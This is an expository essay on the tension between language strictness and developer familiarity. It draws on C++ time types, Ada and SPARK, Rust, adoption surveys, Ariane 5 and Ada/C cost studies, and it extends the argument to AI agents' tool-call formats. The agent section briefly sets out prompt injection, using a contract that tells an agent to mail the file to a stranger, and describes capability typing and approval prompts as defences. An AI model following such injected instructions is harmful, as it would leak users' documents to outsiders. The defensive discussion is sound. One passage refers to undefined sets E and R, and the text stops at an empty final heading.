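# Developer familiarity and safety by construction in programming languages and in the action languages of AI agents

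## What familiarity and safety by construction mean

A programming language has rules that determine which texts count as programs and what each program does. Designers differ over how strict those rules should be. A language is safe by construction against a class of mistakes if its notation cannot express them or if an automatic check rejects any program that contains them before it runs. Some designers aim for this kind of safety, while others stay close to what programmers already know and leave the mistakes possible. Ada, Haskell and Rust came out of the stricter approach, while Solidity, a language for programs that hold and move money on a blockchain, took much of its syntax from JavaScript. AI agents are systems in which a language model acts by writing requests or code, and engineers now face the same choice when they decide what form these may take.

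### One error and four ways to treat it

Suppose a programmer writes `sleep(10)` to make a program pause. Hinnant (2016), in *It's About Time*, a tutorial on the C++ time library, asks whether this means ten seconds, milliseconds or nanoseconds. The line doesn't give the unit. A programmer who expects seconds but calls a function that takes milliseconds gets a pause a thousand times too short, with no error message.

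*Small updates to ensure shell consistency*, a change to the source code of OpenAI's coding agent Codex, fixed a mix-up of this kind. A comment in the code gave the time limit for commands in seconds, but the program counted it in milliseconds. In one version of the tool, the description sent to the model called the argument `timeout` and gave no unit. The change corrected the comment, renamed the argument `timeout_ms` and added a line of explanation for the model.

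A naming convention like this is the easiest treatment to apply, since it only adds a few characters. Anyone who reads the name learns the unit. But the program still accepts `timeout_ms: 10` from a writer who meant ten seconds, so the protection depends on people or models reading the name and acting on it.

A run-time check goes further. The function could reject any limit below a hundred milliseconds, guessing that nobody wants a command to end so soon. That would catch the 10 but miss a 600 that somebody meant as ten minutes, because the number has no unit and the check can only test whether the value is plausible. Run-time checks also take time on every call, and they act only when the faulty line runs, which may first happen while a customer is using the program.

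The compiler, the program that translates source code into something a machine can run, can also catch the error earlier. A type system is the set of rules by which a compiler classifies values and rejects programs that misuse them. Hinnant, Brown and colleagues (2008), in *A Foundation to Sleep On*, proposed giving each unit of time its own type in C++. A value of type `minutes` built from 3 stores only the number 3. The unit is part of the type, so the compiler can check it without adding any work at run time. If a function takes milliseconds, the compiler rejects a plain 10 and accepts `10ms`. It also accepts `10s`, which it converts to ten thousand milliseconds. Conversions from a coarse unit to a finer one are automatic because they are always exact. Programmers have to request the reverse conversion explicitly when working with whole numbers. They also have to add a suffix to each number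 and learn some new vocabulary, and the compiler occasionally rejects a program that would have worked.

Finally, a designer can remove the argument that callers could get wrong. If whoever runs the system sets one time limit for all commands, and the function takes no time argument, no caller can confuse the units. However, a caller with a slow job also cannot ask for more time, and the person who sets the limit can still get it wrong, though only in one place.

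The Linux kernel programmer Rusty Russell (2008) drew up a longer scale of this sort for interfaces between pieces of software, running from 10 ("impossible to get wrong") down to 1. An interface scores 9 if the compiler rejects misuse, 8 if the compiler only warns about it, 6 if the name shows how to use it, and 5 if misuse always fails at run time. Russell ranked run-time failure below a clear name because programmers do not test every path through their code. A name can therefore be worth more in practice than a late check, even though nothing enforces it. Russell also conceded that designers reach the top score only by "greatly restricting your definition of misuse". In an earlier post, *APIs* (2008), Russell gave a reason for accepting such restrictions, writing, "Ease of use attracts users, but difficulty of misuse keeps them alive."

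### What types can record, and what a guarantee leaves out

Besides units, a type system can track effects, meaning anything a piece of code does beyond returning a value, such as writing a file or calling a network. A function with no effects is called pure. Capabilities are one way to control effects. *LACUNA* (2026), a paper on agents that write code, describes a capability as an ordinary value tied to an effect or a resource, such as an open file or a network connection. Code can perform the effect only if it holds the capability, which it cannot forge and must receive from other code. A function that receives no network capability therefore cannot send anything over the network, whatever its author intended. An experimental extension of Scala includes the capabilities a function can reach in the function's type, so the compiler can confirm that the function is pure before anything runs.

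Each of these guarantees covers only a named class of error. The C++ time types rule out confusion between units, yet in *Multiplying integral chrono duration by float has unintuitive behavior* (2016), a thread on a C++ standards forum, a programmer multiplied a duration of 60,000 milliseconds in place by 0.8 and got zero. The duration held a whole number and its multiplication accepted only whole numbers, so C++ silently truncated 0.8 to 0 before multiplying. The program passed the type checks and its units were right, but the resulting duration was wrong. Inria's *Type systems*, an overview by a French research group, calls compile-time type checking an automatic proof of partial correctness, with the stress on "partial".

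Strict languages usually also have an escape hatch, a marked construct that switches off some of the checks. They need one because a checker must reject any program it cannot show to be safe, including some that are safe. Rust, whose main guarantee is memory safety (a program never reads or writes memory it has no right to use), has the `unsafe` block for such cases. Modula-3, a language of the 1980s, confined unsafe features to modules labelled as unsafe. The C++ time library has a milder escape hatch, `count()`, which returns the bare number inside a duration, so the compiler can no longer check the unit.

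If a language has an escape hatch, its guarantee holds for the whole program only if the code behind the hatch is correct, and a person has to vouch for that. A keyword marks this code, so a reviewer can search for it, which is far less work than reading all of a large program for a stray pointer.

### Three kinds of familiarity

A new language can be familiar to a programmer in three ways. Surface familiarity means the programmer recognises the notation, such as braces, keywords and the order of words in a declaration. Semantic familiarity means code does what the programmer expects from other languages. Familiarity of surroundings covers libraries, editors, documentation and colleagues who can answer questions.

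Code that looks the same in two languages can behave differently. *Knowledge Transfer and False Friends*, by Du, Schantong and Siegmund, gives the example of a variable that is declared as an integer and then assigned 10.5. The code is identical in C and Java, but C truncates the value to 10 with a compiler warning, while Java's compiler rejects the program. For a C programmer, the unfamiliar part of Java in this case is its extra safety. Linguists call words that look alike but differ in meaning false friends, and *Understanding conceptual transfer in students learning a new programming language* (Tshukudu, 2022) applied such ideas from second-language research to programming.

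Du and colleagues gave ten short Java programs to university students in the first week of a Java course and asked what each program would do. Most of the students had learned C. Among those who knew C but not Python, 63% read a simple loop correctly and 74% a simple function, but only 12% saw that the assignment of 10.5 was an error. A year later, a new group took the test after a dedicated Java tutorial, and 19% of the C students got that question right. The groups were small, with 16 students in the second year, and Du and colleagues ran no statistical tests. Learners also do not always carry over knowledge that applies in both languages. In C and Java alike, a variable declared inside a loop does not exist outside it, yet only about one C student in six applied the rule in either year.

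Professional programmers make similar mistakes. For *Here We Go Again*, Shrestha, Botta and colleagues (2020) read 450 posts on the question site Stack Overflow in which programmers related one language to another, and found a wrong assumption in 276 of them (61%). People post there when something has gone wrong, so the figure does not measure how often programmers err. The differences between language pairs are more informative. Kotlin runs alongside Java code and shares many of its ideas, but only 6 of 30 posts on that pair held correct assumptions, the lowest count. For PHP and Java, a less obvious match, the count was 16. Programmers coming from Java are surprised, for example, that they cannot extend a Kotlin class unless its author has opened it for extension, because Java allows extension by default.

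Shrestha and colleagues also interviewed 16 professionals who had recently changed languages, and much of what they heard concerned the tools and online help around a language. A programmer who had moved from C++ to TypeScript found that the editor and the system for storing code had changed too. Another was writing Scala in an editor built for Java and kept seeing dialogs about Java settings that matched nothing in the project. A third searched for help with a Python plotting library and found about ten results, compared with a hundred for its counterpart in R.

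A language can therefore be familiar in some ways but not in others. Scala can use Java's libraries and tools while offering constructs that a Java programmer has never seen. Solidity looks like JavaScript but runs on a machine where another program can call back into a function before it has finished.

### The tradeoff

A language is safe by construction against a given error if it rejects every program that contains that error. For most interesting errors, no checker that always finishes can sort every program correctly, so a checker that misses nothing must also reject some harmless programs. According to Inria, finer distinctions between kinds of data catch more mistakes, but they also reject more programs and make code harder to reuse.

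Let *H* be the programs that a particular programmer would write out of habit. Rejecting programs in both *H* and *E* is the benefit the designer wanted. The drawback is that the checker also rejects programs in *H* and *R* but not *E*, which are harmless programs the programmer has always written and must now write differently. The programmer must also add any extra notation the checker needs. Shrestha and colleagues, for example, interviewed a programmer who moved from C# to Rust and found that familiar solutions no longer compiled, because Rust checks which part of a program owns each value. The programmer had to rethink and rewrite them.

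On this account, safety and familiarity tend to conflict, but how much depends on the overlap, which designers can shrink. Type inference, in which the compiler works out most types, removes much of the extra writing. Polymorphism lets one piece of code serve many types, which restores some of the reuse that strict types prevent. The C++ time types add safety with little loss of familiarity. Hinnant and colleagues kept the everyday notation almost identical to that of a library programmers had used for seven years, and described their proposal as purely an addition that would break no existing code, apart from possible name clashes. But because the addition leaves old code alone, the old `sleep(10)` still compiles, and the guarantee protects only those who choose the new types.

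### When the programmer is a model

A large language model is a program trained on a great deal of text to produce more of it, and it becomes an agent when it can also act. Anthropic's *Building effective agents* reserves the term for systems in which the model decides what steps to take and which tools to use, and describes the usual design as a model using tools in a loop. An engineer first writes a tool interface, which lists operations such as "read a file" or "run a command" and the arguments each one takes. To make a tool call, the model writes a request in an agreed format, commonly JSON, a plain notation for labelled data. Ordinary software carries out the request and adds the result to the model's input, and the model then decides what to do next. In some systems the model instead writes a short program, called a code action, that calls several tools at once. Whichever format the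 model uses is the agent's action language, which can be strict or lax like any other language.

Agents are exposed to prompt injection, which is text placed in their input to redirect what they do. Human programmers seldom pose this danger. The text may come from a hostile user or from a web page or document that the agent reads. For example, a contract under review could contain a line telling the agent to mail the file to a stranger. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, accept that general programming needs escape hatches, or ways around the type system, but forbid them in code that an agent writes, because a hijacked model could use them too.

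With AI agents, the developer's role is also divided. The model writes the action, an engineer builds the interface, and somebody may have to review the result. For a model, the counterpart of familiarity is training exposure, meaning the amount of code in a given language or format in its training data. In a guide first published in December 2024, Anthropic advises engineers to keep tool formats close to text that occurs naturally on the internet. It warns that diffs are hard for models to write because the header must state how many lines will change before the new lines are written. Programmers read diffs every day when they review each other's work, so a format that suits the reviewer can still be difficult for the model.

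A model may have little trouble with restrictions that would irritate a person. While building a coding agent, Anthropic's engineers saw the model make mistakes with relative file paths, which start from the current folder, after it had moved to a different folder. They changed the tool to require absolute paths, which give the full location. People tend to avoid these because they are long, but the model used them without error.

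The engineer who builds the interface has habits from ordinary languages and libraries, and must write the types or checks that a stricter design needs. The reviewer may not know the languages, libraries or types involved. According to OpenAI's documentation, Codex in automatic mode can edit files and run commands in its working folder, but must ask a person before editing files elsewhere or running a command that needs the network. Odersky and colleagues object that people tire of such requests and stop paying attention to them. They argue that typed interfaces are concise and readable for humans, unlike today's JSON tool descriptions. They write those interfaces in Scala, which Odersky designed, and a reviewer who has never seen a Scala type may find the JSON easier.

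## How programmers choose a language

A strict compiler helps only the people who use its language, and a team with working code in another language has to give something up to switch. Erik Meijer, a language designer who had long promoted the functional language Haskell, used an idea from Pip Coburn's business book *The Change Function* to explain why so few teams switch. According to *Why your favorite language is unpopular* (2008), a blog post about one of his talks, Meijer argued that people change tools when they have a pressing problem and the change looks easy enough, whereas technologists tend to believe that a tool ten times better than its rivals will catch on.

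### The change function

Coburn's rule compares the crisis that a technology would solve with the pain of adopting it, both as the user perceives them. People adopt the technology only if

perceived crisis ÷ perceived pain of adoption > 1.

For a programming language, the pain includes time spent learning, code to rewrite and libraries to replace.

The time needed to switch languages can strongly affect the choice, as an example with invented figures shows. A team of ten programmers loses 60 working days a year to one class of error. Adopting a new language that rules out these errors would take 300 working days, with 20 for each programmer to learn it and 100 to replace the team's libraries. A checker for their present language would rule out the same errors and take 30 days to adopt, with one day of training for each programmer and 20 days to add annotations.

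| Option | Days the team expects to save in a year | Days the change costs | Ratio |
|---|---|---|---|
| New language | 60 | 300 | 0.2 |
| Checker for the present language | 60 | 30 | 2.0 |
| Checker, if the team underestimates its losses | 24 | 30 | 0.8 |

The new language and the checker bring the same gain in safety, but only the checker meets Coburn's rule. If nobody has counted the lost days and the team guesses 24, the checker fails too. The result also depends on the period, which Coburn's rule doesn't specify. Over six years, the new language would save 360 days for the same 300, a ratio of 1.2.

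The blog post applies the rule to several languages. Visual Basic made it easy to write Windows applications, and anyone with Excel could start by pressing two keys. Java spared programmers crashes from memory errors and bad pointers, and its syntax resembled that of C++. Lisp had powerful features that few people felt they needed, and it was painful to adopt. But the post judges these languages after their outcomes were known, and some commenters credited Java's success to marketing or university teaching instead. The rule predicts little unless somebody measures the crisis and the pain of adoption beforehand.

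In *Socio-PLT*, a paper on the sociology of programming languages, Meyerovich and Rabkin (2012) call the change function "insightful but simplistic", partly because it explains little about competition between technologies. They recommend starting from Everett Rogers's research on how innovations spread. In his model, a person hears of an innovation, becomes interested, decides whether to adopt it, tries it and confirms the decision, and can stop at any step. People adopt an innovation more readily if it improves on what they have, fits their needs and beliefs, is simple, is easy to try and has visible results. Meyerovich and Rabkin found that language researchers focus on the first of these factors and give the others much less attention. A familiar language has an advantage even if it is no better than its rivals, because it fits existing habits and is easier to try.

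### What programmers did and what they reported

Meyerovich and Rabkin studied these choices quantitatively in *Empirical Analysis of Programming Language Adoption* (2013). They used surveys of roughly 1,000 to 13,000 people and descriptions of over 200,000 projects from SourceForge, the main host of open-source software for most of the study period, 2000 to 2010. They checked some results against another database of 590,000 projects.

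Six languages (Java, C++, PHP, C, Python and C#) accounted for 75% of the SourceForge projects, and twenty accounted for 95%. Many other languages remained in use among small groups of programmers, usually for a few kinds of application. Even in those applications, the generally popular languages tended to have more users than the specialised ones.

Meyerovich and Rabkin studied developers who had worked on several projects, comparing the language of each project with that of the next. A developer starting from a language picked at random kept it 18% of the time and moved to one of the top six languages 52% of the time. This calculation weights all languages equally, however rare, so 18% is not the share of all developers who kept their language. A model that used only a language's popularity and the developer's previous language predicted over 75% of the choices.

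Developers seldom moved between Scheme and Lisp, or among Ruby, Python and Perl, although the languages in each group are similar. Meyerovich and Rabkin concluded that a developer's background and technical surroundings influence these moves more than similarity does. They advise anyone promoting a language to choose an application area and win over the programmers who work in it. On this evidence, a designer who borrows the syntax of a popular language can't count on attracting its users.

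Popularity predicts which language programmers choose but doesn't explain why, since a popular language also has more libraries and more colleagues who know it. To find the reasons, Meyerovich and Rabkin surveyed 1,679 people, most of whom found the survey through technology news sites, and asked how strongly each of 14 factors had influenced the choice of language for their latest project. Open-source libraries ranked first, and more than 60% of respondents said they had a medium or strong influence. The next four factors were existing code, the group's earlier use of the language, the respondent's own familiarity with it, and the team's familiarity with it. Safety and correctness ranked tenth, and simplicity ranked last, at about 25%.

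Respondents in companies with more than 100 employees gave more weight to correctness than those in smaller companies did. They also gave more weight to existing code and to what their group already knew. Large companies may therefore want a safer language more than small ones do but find it harder to adopt one.

Another possible explanation for safety's low rank is that four of the six most popular languages, Java, PHP, Python and C#, manage memory automatically. The survey measured which factors decided a choice, so someone choosing among those four had little reason to name memory safety, even if they would have missed it.

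Another group, students of an online course on web software, gave their opinions about types. Of these students, 96 described themselves as professional developers. Only 36% of the professionals saw the value of static types, which a compiler checks before the program runs, while 62% saw the value of unit tests, which are short programs that run a piece of code and check its result. Only 8% thought that types were valuable mostly for finding bugs.

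Meyerovich and Rabkin conclude that developers value types more for expressiveness than for checking correctness. The survey answers are less clear, since 45% of the professionals said types improved readability and 44% said they improved safety, each with a margin of error of about ten points. The course also taught Ruby, which has no compile-time type checking, so it probably attracted people used to working without it. A separate online poll supports the conclusion better. Enjoyment of a language had a correlation of 0.76 with calling it expressive, but only 0.38 with saying it had a strong static type system.

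How a question named a feature also affected the answers. Students in the course rated class interfaces far above static types, though programmers mostly use interfaces in languages that have static types. A designer might therefore win more support for a check by presenting it as a way to organise a program.

All of these surveys relied on volunteers, mainly Americans and other English speakers, many of them enthusiasts who read technology blogs. People may also misremember why they chose a language, or give a respectable reason for a choice their manager made. The record of moves between projects avoids that problem, but it covers only open-source work. Companies may keep using obscure languages for longer than open-source projects do, and makers of aircraft or medical devices, who have formal safety duties, would hardly appear in the record.

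One respondent in five had learned the main language of their latest project while working on it. Yet older and younger programmers both knew about six languages well on average, which suggests that people forget old languages as they learn new ones. Education had some lasting effect. Of the respondents who had studied a functional language at school, 40% knew one, compared with 15% of those who had not.

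### Why prevented errors persuade few people

In their 2012 paper, Meyerovich and Rabkin suggested that one reason such features have little appeal is that programmers often can't see the benefit directly or soon after adopting them. Their example is static types. People try out a new language on small programs, where tests may catch most mistakes, but the benefits of types may appear only in a large system that several people maintain for years. The trial therefore shows programmers all the extra work that types require but little of their benefit.

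Public health workers have long dealt with this difficulty. Researchers who study how ideas spread use the term "preventive innovations" for those that people adopt now to make some later harm less likely. Meyerovich and Rabkin draw on an experiment that Kelly and colleagues published in 1992, during the HIV epidemic in American cities. Most people surveyed in bars already knew how to protect themselves, yet between 31% and 49% of those at risk reported very dangerous behaviour in the previous two months. The researchers asked bartenders to identify popular customers and taught them, in four 90-minute sessions, how to recommend safer behaviour to their peers. Dangerous behaviour then fell by 15% to 24% on average.

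Meyerovich and Rabkin suspect that most professional programmers have heard of functional languages and that more information would change little. They think a respected colleague might have more influence. They drew this hypothesis by analogy and did not test it on programmers.

The benefit of safety by construction is hard for programmers to see. When a compiler rejects a faulty line, the programmer sees an error message and loses a few minutes, but the crash or theft that the line would have caused never happens. A team with no such crashes can't easily tell whether the reason is the language, its own care or luck. An organisation that counts failures across many projects is more likely to be able to tell, and it can also require a language that individual programmers would not have picked.

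That difference can be harder to interpret when a language is difficult to learn. Meyerovich and Rabkin cite Iannaccone's research on strict religious groups, whose demanding rules drive away half-hearted members and leave a more committed community. They suggest that the correctness and productivity gains credited to functional languages may come more from the people who use them than from the languages. If so, a low bug rate in a demanding language partly reflects who was willing to learn it, and a team ordered to switch might not get the same result.

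### Syntax and old habits

Many designers try to make their languages easier to start using by borrowing familiar notation. Stefik and Siebert (2013), in *An Empirical Investigation into Programming Language Syntax*, tested how much common notations help beginners. They assigned each of 72 students who had never programmed to one of six languages and gave them six short tasks. The students had sample programs for the first three tasks but no explanation of what each line did. One of the languages, Randomo, was a placebo that Stefik and Siebert made by replacing most of the keywords in their own language, Quorum, with random characters.

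Students using Ruby got 56% of the elements of their programs right on average, compared with 53% for Python, 51% for Quorum, 43% for Perl, 40% for Java and 34% for Randomo, the placebo. The scores for Perl and Java, which follow the C tradition of braces and semicolons, were not significantly higher than Randomo's. With about twelve students per language, the experiment could have missed a modest advantage, but some conventions that professionals take for granted clearly confused the beginners. Of the 48 students using Java, Perl, Python or Ruby, only one correctly wrote the double equals sign that tests whether two values are equal. In Quorum, which uses a single equals sign for this test, 67% got it right.

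Programmers and newcomers judge the same notation differently. In a survey that preceded the experiment, Stefik and Siebert asked students to rate how intuitive pieces of code were, from 0 to 10. Students with programming experience gave a C-style `while` loop 7.8, and those without gave it 5.2. Ratings of C++ code rose by about half a point for each year of experience with C++, although experience accounted for only about 9% of the variation. People thus seem to acquire surface familiarity through experience, and a designer who copies C's notation helps programmers who already know it much more than newcomers.

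The beginners also had trouble with types, placing type declarations correctly only about half the time. But Stefik and Siebert cite other experiments in which static types helped experienced programmers work faster, and they advise keeping the checks while letting the compiler infer most types inside a function. Because the difficulty of types comes before the benefit, a short trial is a poor test of their value.

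Experience in one language can help or mislead a programmer in the next. Among the Stack Overflow posts that Shrestha and colleagues examined, a Java programmer guessed correctly that Kotlin could work out a variable's type without a declaration. An R programmer tried to change selected values in a Python table, but the Python expression returned a copy, so the assignment did not work as it would have in R. A PHP programmer wanted to store a user's session in JavaScript as PHP does. PHP keeps session data on the server, and the reply warned that a browser can't hold it securely.

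Most of the professionals whom Shrestha and colleagues interviewed had no formal training in their new language. They learned features as they needed them and looked for counterparts to what they already knew, which saves time when a counterpart exists. The interviews had no comparison group, so they show what goes wrong but not how much time programmers lose. *It's Like Python But* (2018) presents a possible remedy, a training tool that shows code in two languages, points out what carries over and warns of likely misconceptions. Its designers tried it with 20 participants from a graduate course.

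Old habits can cause even more trouble in a stricter language, as the C# programmer who moved to Rust found. *The Usability of Advanced Type Systems* (2023) suggests that these habits are part of what makes Rust hard to learn. Beginners don't have them to unlearn, but they also have less reason to know what the rules prevent.

### Whether AI tools favour typed languages

AI coding tools could change both sides of Coburn's comparison. An assistant can write type declarations and explain unfamiliar notation, which reduces the work of using a strict language. It can also produce more code than anyone has time to read closely, which makes automatic checks more useful.

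GitHub, the largest host of open-source code, believes such a shift is under way. Its evidence is that TypeScript, a version of JavaScript with added types, became the most-used language on the site for the first time in August 2025. GitHub's *How AI is reshaping developer choice (and Octoverse data proves it)* argues that developers come to associate certain technologies with convenience and then keep choosing them. GitHub sells an AI coding assistant, so it has an interest in this conclusion.

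The number of TypeScript contributors on GitHub rose by 66% in a year to 2.63 million, according to Linuxiac's *TypeScript Overtakes Python to Become GitHub's #1 Programming Language in 2025* (2025). GitHub as a whole grew more slowly. It's FOSS's *GitHub's 2025 Report Reveals Some Surprising Developer Trends* (2025) lists over 180 million developers, 36 million of them new, which implies growth of about a quarter. Registered developers and active contributors are different groups, but the gap is wide enough to suggest that GitHub's overall growth doesn't fully explain TypeScript's.

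It is less clear that developers turned to types in general, or that AI led them to do so. TypeScript led Python by only about 42,000 contributors, less than 2% of Python's total. Linuxiac reports that Python and JavaScript, neither of which requires programmers to declare types, also kept growing strongly. If assistants make TypeScript easier to learn, they make Python easier to learn too, and models have been trained on a great deal of code in both.

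TypeScript also had advantages that don't depend on AI. A JavaScript team that adopts it can keep its libraries and most of its code, so the change function would predict high adoption even without AI assistants. Web frameworks that generate new projects in TypeScript would add to its count even if developers never weighed the merits of types. GitHub's *What the fastest-growing tools reveal about how software is being built* stresses reduced friction, which fits the view that developers adopted TypeScript because switching was easy at least as well as the view that they wanted safety.

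GitHub's figures show that one typed language has grown, but a count of contributors can't explain why. A fair test of the cause would compare similar developers starting new projects with and without AI assistants, and would check whether other typed languages, such as Java, C# and Go, also gained. It would also have to separate the developer's choice from the assistant's, since a person who accepts a generated project may never have chosen its language.

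## Ada, a safe language adopted by order

Most of the programmers in these surveys had some say over which language they used, and safety ranked low among their reasons for choosing one. The US Department of Defense, by contrast, paid for the design of Ada, a language with many built-in checks, and required it for most of the department's new software from 1987 to 1997.

### What Ada checks

Suppose a C program counts good and bad items and stores both counts, and a limit for each, as plain integers. AdaCore, a company that sells Ada tools, uses this case to show a slip that a C compiler accepts:

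```c
int goodcount, badcount, g_limit, b_limit;
...
if (goodcount == b_limit) { ... }   /* should be g_limit */
```

An Ada programmer can declare two types that both hold integers but do not mix:

```ada
type Goods is new Integer;
type Bads  is new Integer;

Good_Count, G_Limit : Goods;
Bad_Count,  B_Limit : Bads;
...
if Good_Count = B_Limit then   -- the compiler rejects this line
```

As with the C++ time types, the distinction adds no work at run time and protects only programmers who choose to use it. Anyone who does want to compare the two can write an explicit conversion, `Goods (B_Limit)`.

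A type can also limit its values to a range. EmbeddedRelated, a site for engineers who program devices, gives the example `type Passenger_Count is new Integer range 0 .. 853`, where 853 is the most passengers an Airbus A380 can hold. If a program adds 500 to 400 and stores the result as a `Passenger_Count`, Ada raises an error named `Constraint_Error`. This usually happens while the program is running, because the numbers it will receive are not known when it is compiled.

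Ada makes similar run-time checks on array positions and on pointers that may point to nothing, and the programmer can write code to respond when a check fails. In C, the same mistakes can cause a program to read or overwrite other data without warning. *Ada and Beyond* (1997), written for the Defense Department by the National Research Council, which advises the US government, judged Ada superior to C, C++ and the then-new Java for critical real-time systems, partly because of these checks.

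Larger Ada programs consist of packages. Each package has a specification, which lists the types and operations that other code may use, and a body, which contains the code that implements them. The compiler checks every use of a package against its specification, even before anyone has written the body. Teams on a large project can therefore find out early whether their parts fit together.

Ada has escape hatches too. Programmers can switch off the run-time checks to make a program run faster, and they can use a procedure named `Unchecked_Deallocation` to free memory even if other code still holds a pointer to it.

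SPARK, a subset of Ada, lets programmers prove before a program runs that its run-time checks will never fail. It excludes or restricts features that make programs hard to reason about. Programmers also add contracts, which state what must be true before a piece of code runs and what will be true afterwards.

When a SPARK function adds two `Passenger_Count` values, the tools report that they cannot prove the sum will always fit the range. If the programmer adds a precondition that the sum is at most 853, the function passes, but the tools must then prove that every call to it from elsewhere in the program meets the precondition. Contracts can also describe the result a function should compute, so that the tools can check more than the absence of crashes. Contracts take effort to write, and a proof is reliable only if the conditions it assumes are true.

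### The Ariane 5 failure

On 4 June 1996 the first Ariane 5 rocket veered off course and exploded about 40 seconds into its flight sequence. Its guidance units ran Ada software. The official inquiry's report, *Ariane 5 Flight 501 Failure* (Lions, 1996), traced the loss to a number that had grown too large for its type.

The software came from Ariane 4. One part of it aligned the guidance unit before launch and kept running for about 40 seconds after lift-off, so that ground crews could restart the countdown quickly after a late hold. Ariane 5 didn't need this function, but its engineers kept it so that the two rockets would have common software. It converted a value related to horizontal velocity from a floating-point number to an integer. The value stayed within the integer's range on Ariane 4, but Ariane 5 built up horizontal velocity five times as fast, and about 30 seconds after lift-off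 the value was too large to fit.

Engineers had looked for this kind of error and found seven variables at risk. They protected only four, to keep the computer's workload below 80%. They reasoned that the other three either had physical limits or a large safety margin. Lions found no evidence that anyone had tested this reasoning against trajectory data.

The software detected the error and raised an exception. But the specification required the computer to shut down after any exception, because the designers expected exceptions to come from random hardware faults that a backup unit could handle. The backup ran the same software and had already failed for the same reason about 0.05 seconds earlier. The main computer then treated diagnostic data from the failed unit as flight data and swung the engine nozzles to correct a deviation that had not occurred.

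Ada's run-time check caught the bad value. The engineers had left the conversion unprotected, and no language rule could determine what a rocket should do when its guidance software fails. A proof in the style of SPARK would have required them to state a bound on the horizontal velocity. If they had used the Ariane 4 bound, the proof would have succeeded and the rocket would still have been lost. The project's partners had in fact agreed to leave the Ariane 5 trajectory out of the unit's specification.

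Investigators later reproduced the failure by running the software with the real trajectory. The European Space Agency's *Ariane 501* (1996) lists the agency's remedies, which include running such simulations and no longer shutting down the processor when it detects a fault.

### How the order worked

The Defense Department wanted a common language mainly to save money. According to the National Research Council, the cost of the department's computer systems rose by 51% between 1968 and 1973, even though hardware became much cheaper. A widely cited estimate put the number of languages and dialects in those systems at 450 or more, though nobody had made a full count. Often only the original contractor could maintain a system.

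The department reviewed existing languages and decided that none met the needs of computers inside weapons and other equipment. In June 1978 a working group published Steelman, the final requirements for a new language, according to *Steelman On-Line*. A team at the French company Cii-Honeywell Bull produced the winning design, and the department named it after the mathematician Ada Lovelace. In 1983 a senior official ordered its use in all new mission-critical software, but compilers were immature and many contracts still went to projects that used other languages.

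The Department of Defense widened the rule in April 1987. Its *Computer Programming Language Policy* (1987) made Ada the single language for weapons, intelligence systems and the command of forces. For other software, developers could choose one of nine approved alternatives if it would cost less over the system's lifetime. C was not among the nine, so a project needed a waiver to use it, and the request had to include an analysis of lifetime costs and risks. Commercial software that the department did not modify or maintain needed no waiver.

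Many projects ignored the rule. In 1994, Ada made up 33% of the department's mission-critical code in general-purpose languages, and C made up 22%. Some of the C may have predated the rule, but the services had granted only 31 waivers since 1992, even though they approved most requests. The National Research Council concluded that few of the projects that avoided Ada had requested a waiver.

Complying with the rule could also cause problems. Some managers feared that requesting a waiver would reflect badly on them, so they used Ada where another language would have been cheaper. Others passed over good tools for building graphical interfaces because the tools did not produce Ada. The rule also applied to each system as a whole, so a project with new flight software, an old simulator in C and test equipment in several languages had to write everything in Ada or seek a waiver for all of it.

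### The evidence on cost and defects

In 1996 Emmett Paige, the assistant secretary responsible for the policy, asked the National Research Council to review it. Its committee looked for projects that would show whether Ada had been worth the trouble. Stephen Zeigler of Rational, a company that sold programming tools, provided the most useful comparison. The software analysts Reifer and Jones supplied figures from databases that outsiders could not inspect. The costs below are per line of code and the defects per thousand lines, except in the last row, where both are per function point. A function point is a measure of what software does for its users.

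| Software | Cost, Ada | Cost, C | Defects, Ada | Defects, C |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Compilers and tools (Zeigler) | $6.60 | $10.50 | 0.10 | 0.68 |
| Military information systems (Reifer) | $30 | $25 | 3.0 | 6.0 |
| Embedded weapon systems (Reifer) | $150 | $175 | 0.3 | 0.8 |
| Telecommunications (Jones) | $1,760 | $2,966 | 0.17 | 0.29 |

Ada had fewer defects than C in every row, but it cost more in military information systems. Comparisons per line of code are also unreliable, because a line of one language may do more than a line of another. In Jones's data, C took from 60 to 170 lines per function point. The National Research Council suspected that the differences Jones found between languages mostly reflected the average rates used to convert between lines of code and function points.

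According to NASA's records, its Ada teams at first worked faster and more cheaply than its Fortran teams because they reused more code. The Fortran teams then adopted the same approach to reuse and made similar gains, so the method explained much of the saving. But Ada code still had less than half the defect rate of Fortran code, at 2.1 per thousand lines against 4.8, and the language may have had more to do with that difference.

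Boeing, however, found no correlation between a system's language and the number of problems in it. The company had chosen Ada in 1985 without being ordered to, and 70% of the code its suppliers developed for the 777 airliner was in Ada.

The committee concluded that the data supported Ada's advantage in reliability but were too weak to establish an advantage in cost. It also warned that perhaps only the good projects had reported results. Two members' firms, Rational and Intermetrics, sold Ada products. Route Fifty's *Unlock Ada's grip on DOD, report urges* (1996) reported that the committee had no military representatives.

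### Zeigler's comparison

*Comparing Development Costs of C and Ada* (Zeigler, 1995) uses unusually good records. Verdix, which merged into Rational in 1994, had logged every change to its compilers and related tools since 1983. By October 1994 the product contained 1.5 million lines of C and 1.3 million of Ada, excluding comments and blank lines. All but two of its 62 programmers had worked in both languages, with the same tools and design methods. Customers had found 1,020 bugs in the C code and 122 in the Ada code, and a new feature had cost 1.63 times as much in C.

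The National Research Council put the cost ratio at only 1.37, after adjusting for 16% more lines per feature in Ada. Its figures of 94 lines per feature in C and 109 in Ada equal the sums of Zeigler's separate averages for interface files and for the code that implements them. Zeigler's overall totals give about 57 lines per feature in C and 55 in Ada, so no adjustment is needed, which supports the higher ratio.

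More seriously, Verdix did not assign languages to tasks at random. It started in C because no good Ada compiler existed, so the oldest and largest parts of the product were in C. When Zeigler compared only the most expensive parts in each language, the ratio of bug fixes per feature fell from about 2:1 to 1.6:1.

The company also replaced its C optimizer, the part of a compiler that makes programs faster, with one written in Ada. Customers reported 31 bugs in four years of using the C version and 10 in four years of using the Ada version. But different people wrote the Ada version, using a new design, and they could learn from the C version.

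Other circumstances favoured C. Three quarters of the people Verdix hired had substantial experience with C, and fewer than a quarter had substantial experience with Ada. The programmers also wrote more checks by hand in the C code because the language did not supply them.

A critic in the newsgroup thread *Justifying Development tools* objected that nobody can take an uncontrolled history with seven variables and correct for each separately afterwards. That is a fair objection to the exact ratios, but an eightfold difference in customer-reported bugs between code bases of similar size is harder to explain away. The age of the C code could account for part of it. Zeigler, whose employer sold Ada tools, still ranked design, testing and the skill of programmers and managers above the choice of language, and doubted that the results apply as well to projects shorter than a year.

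### Why Ada stayed in its niche

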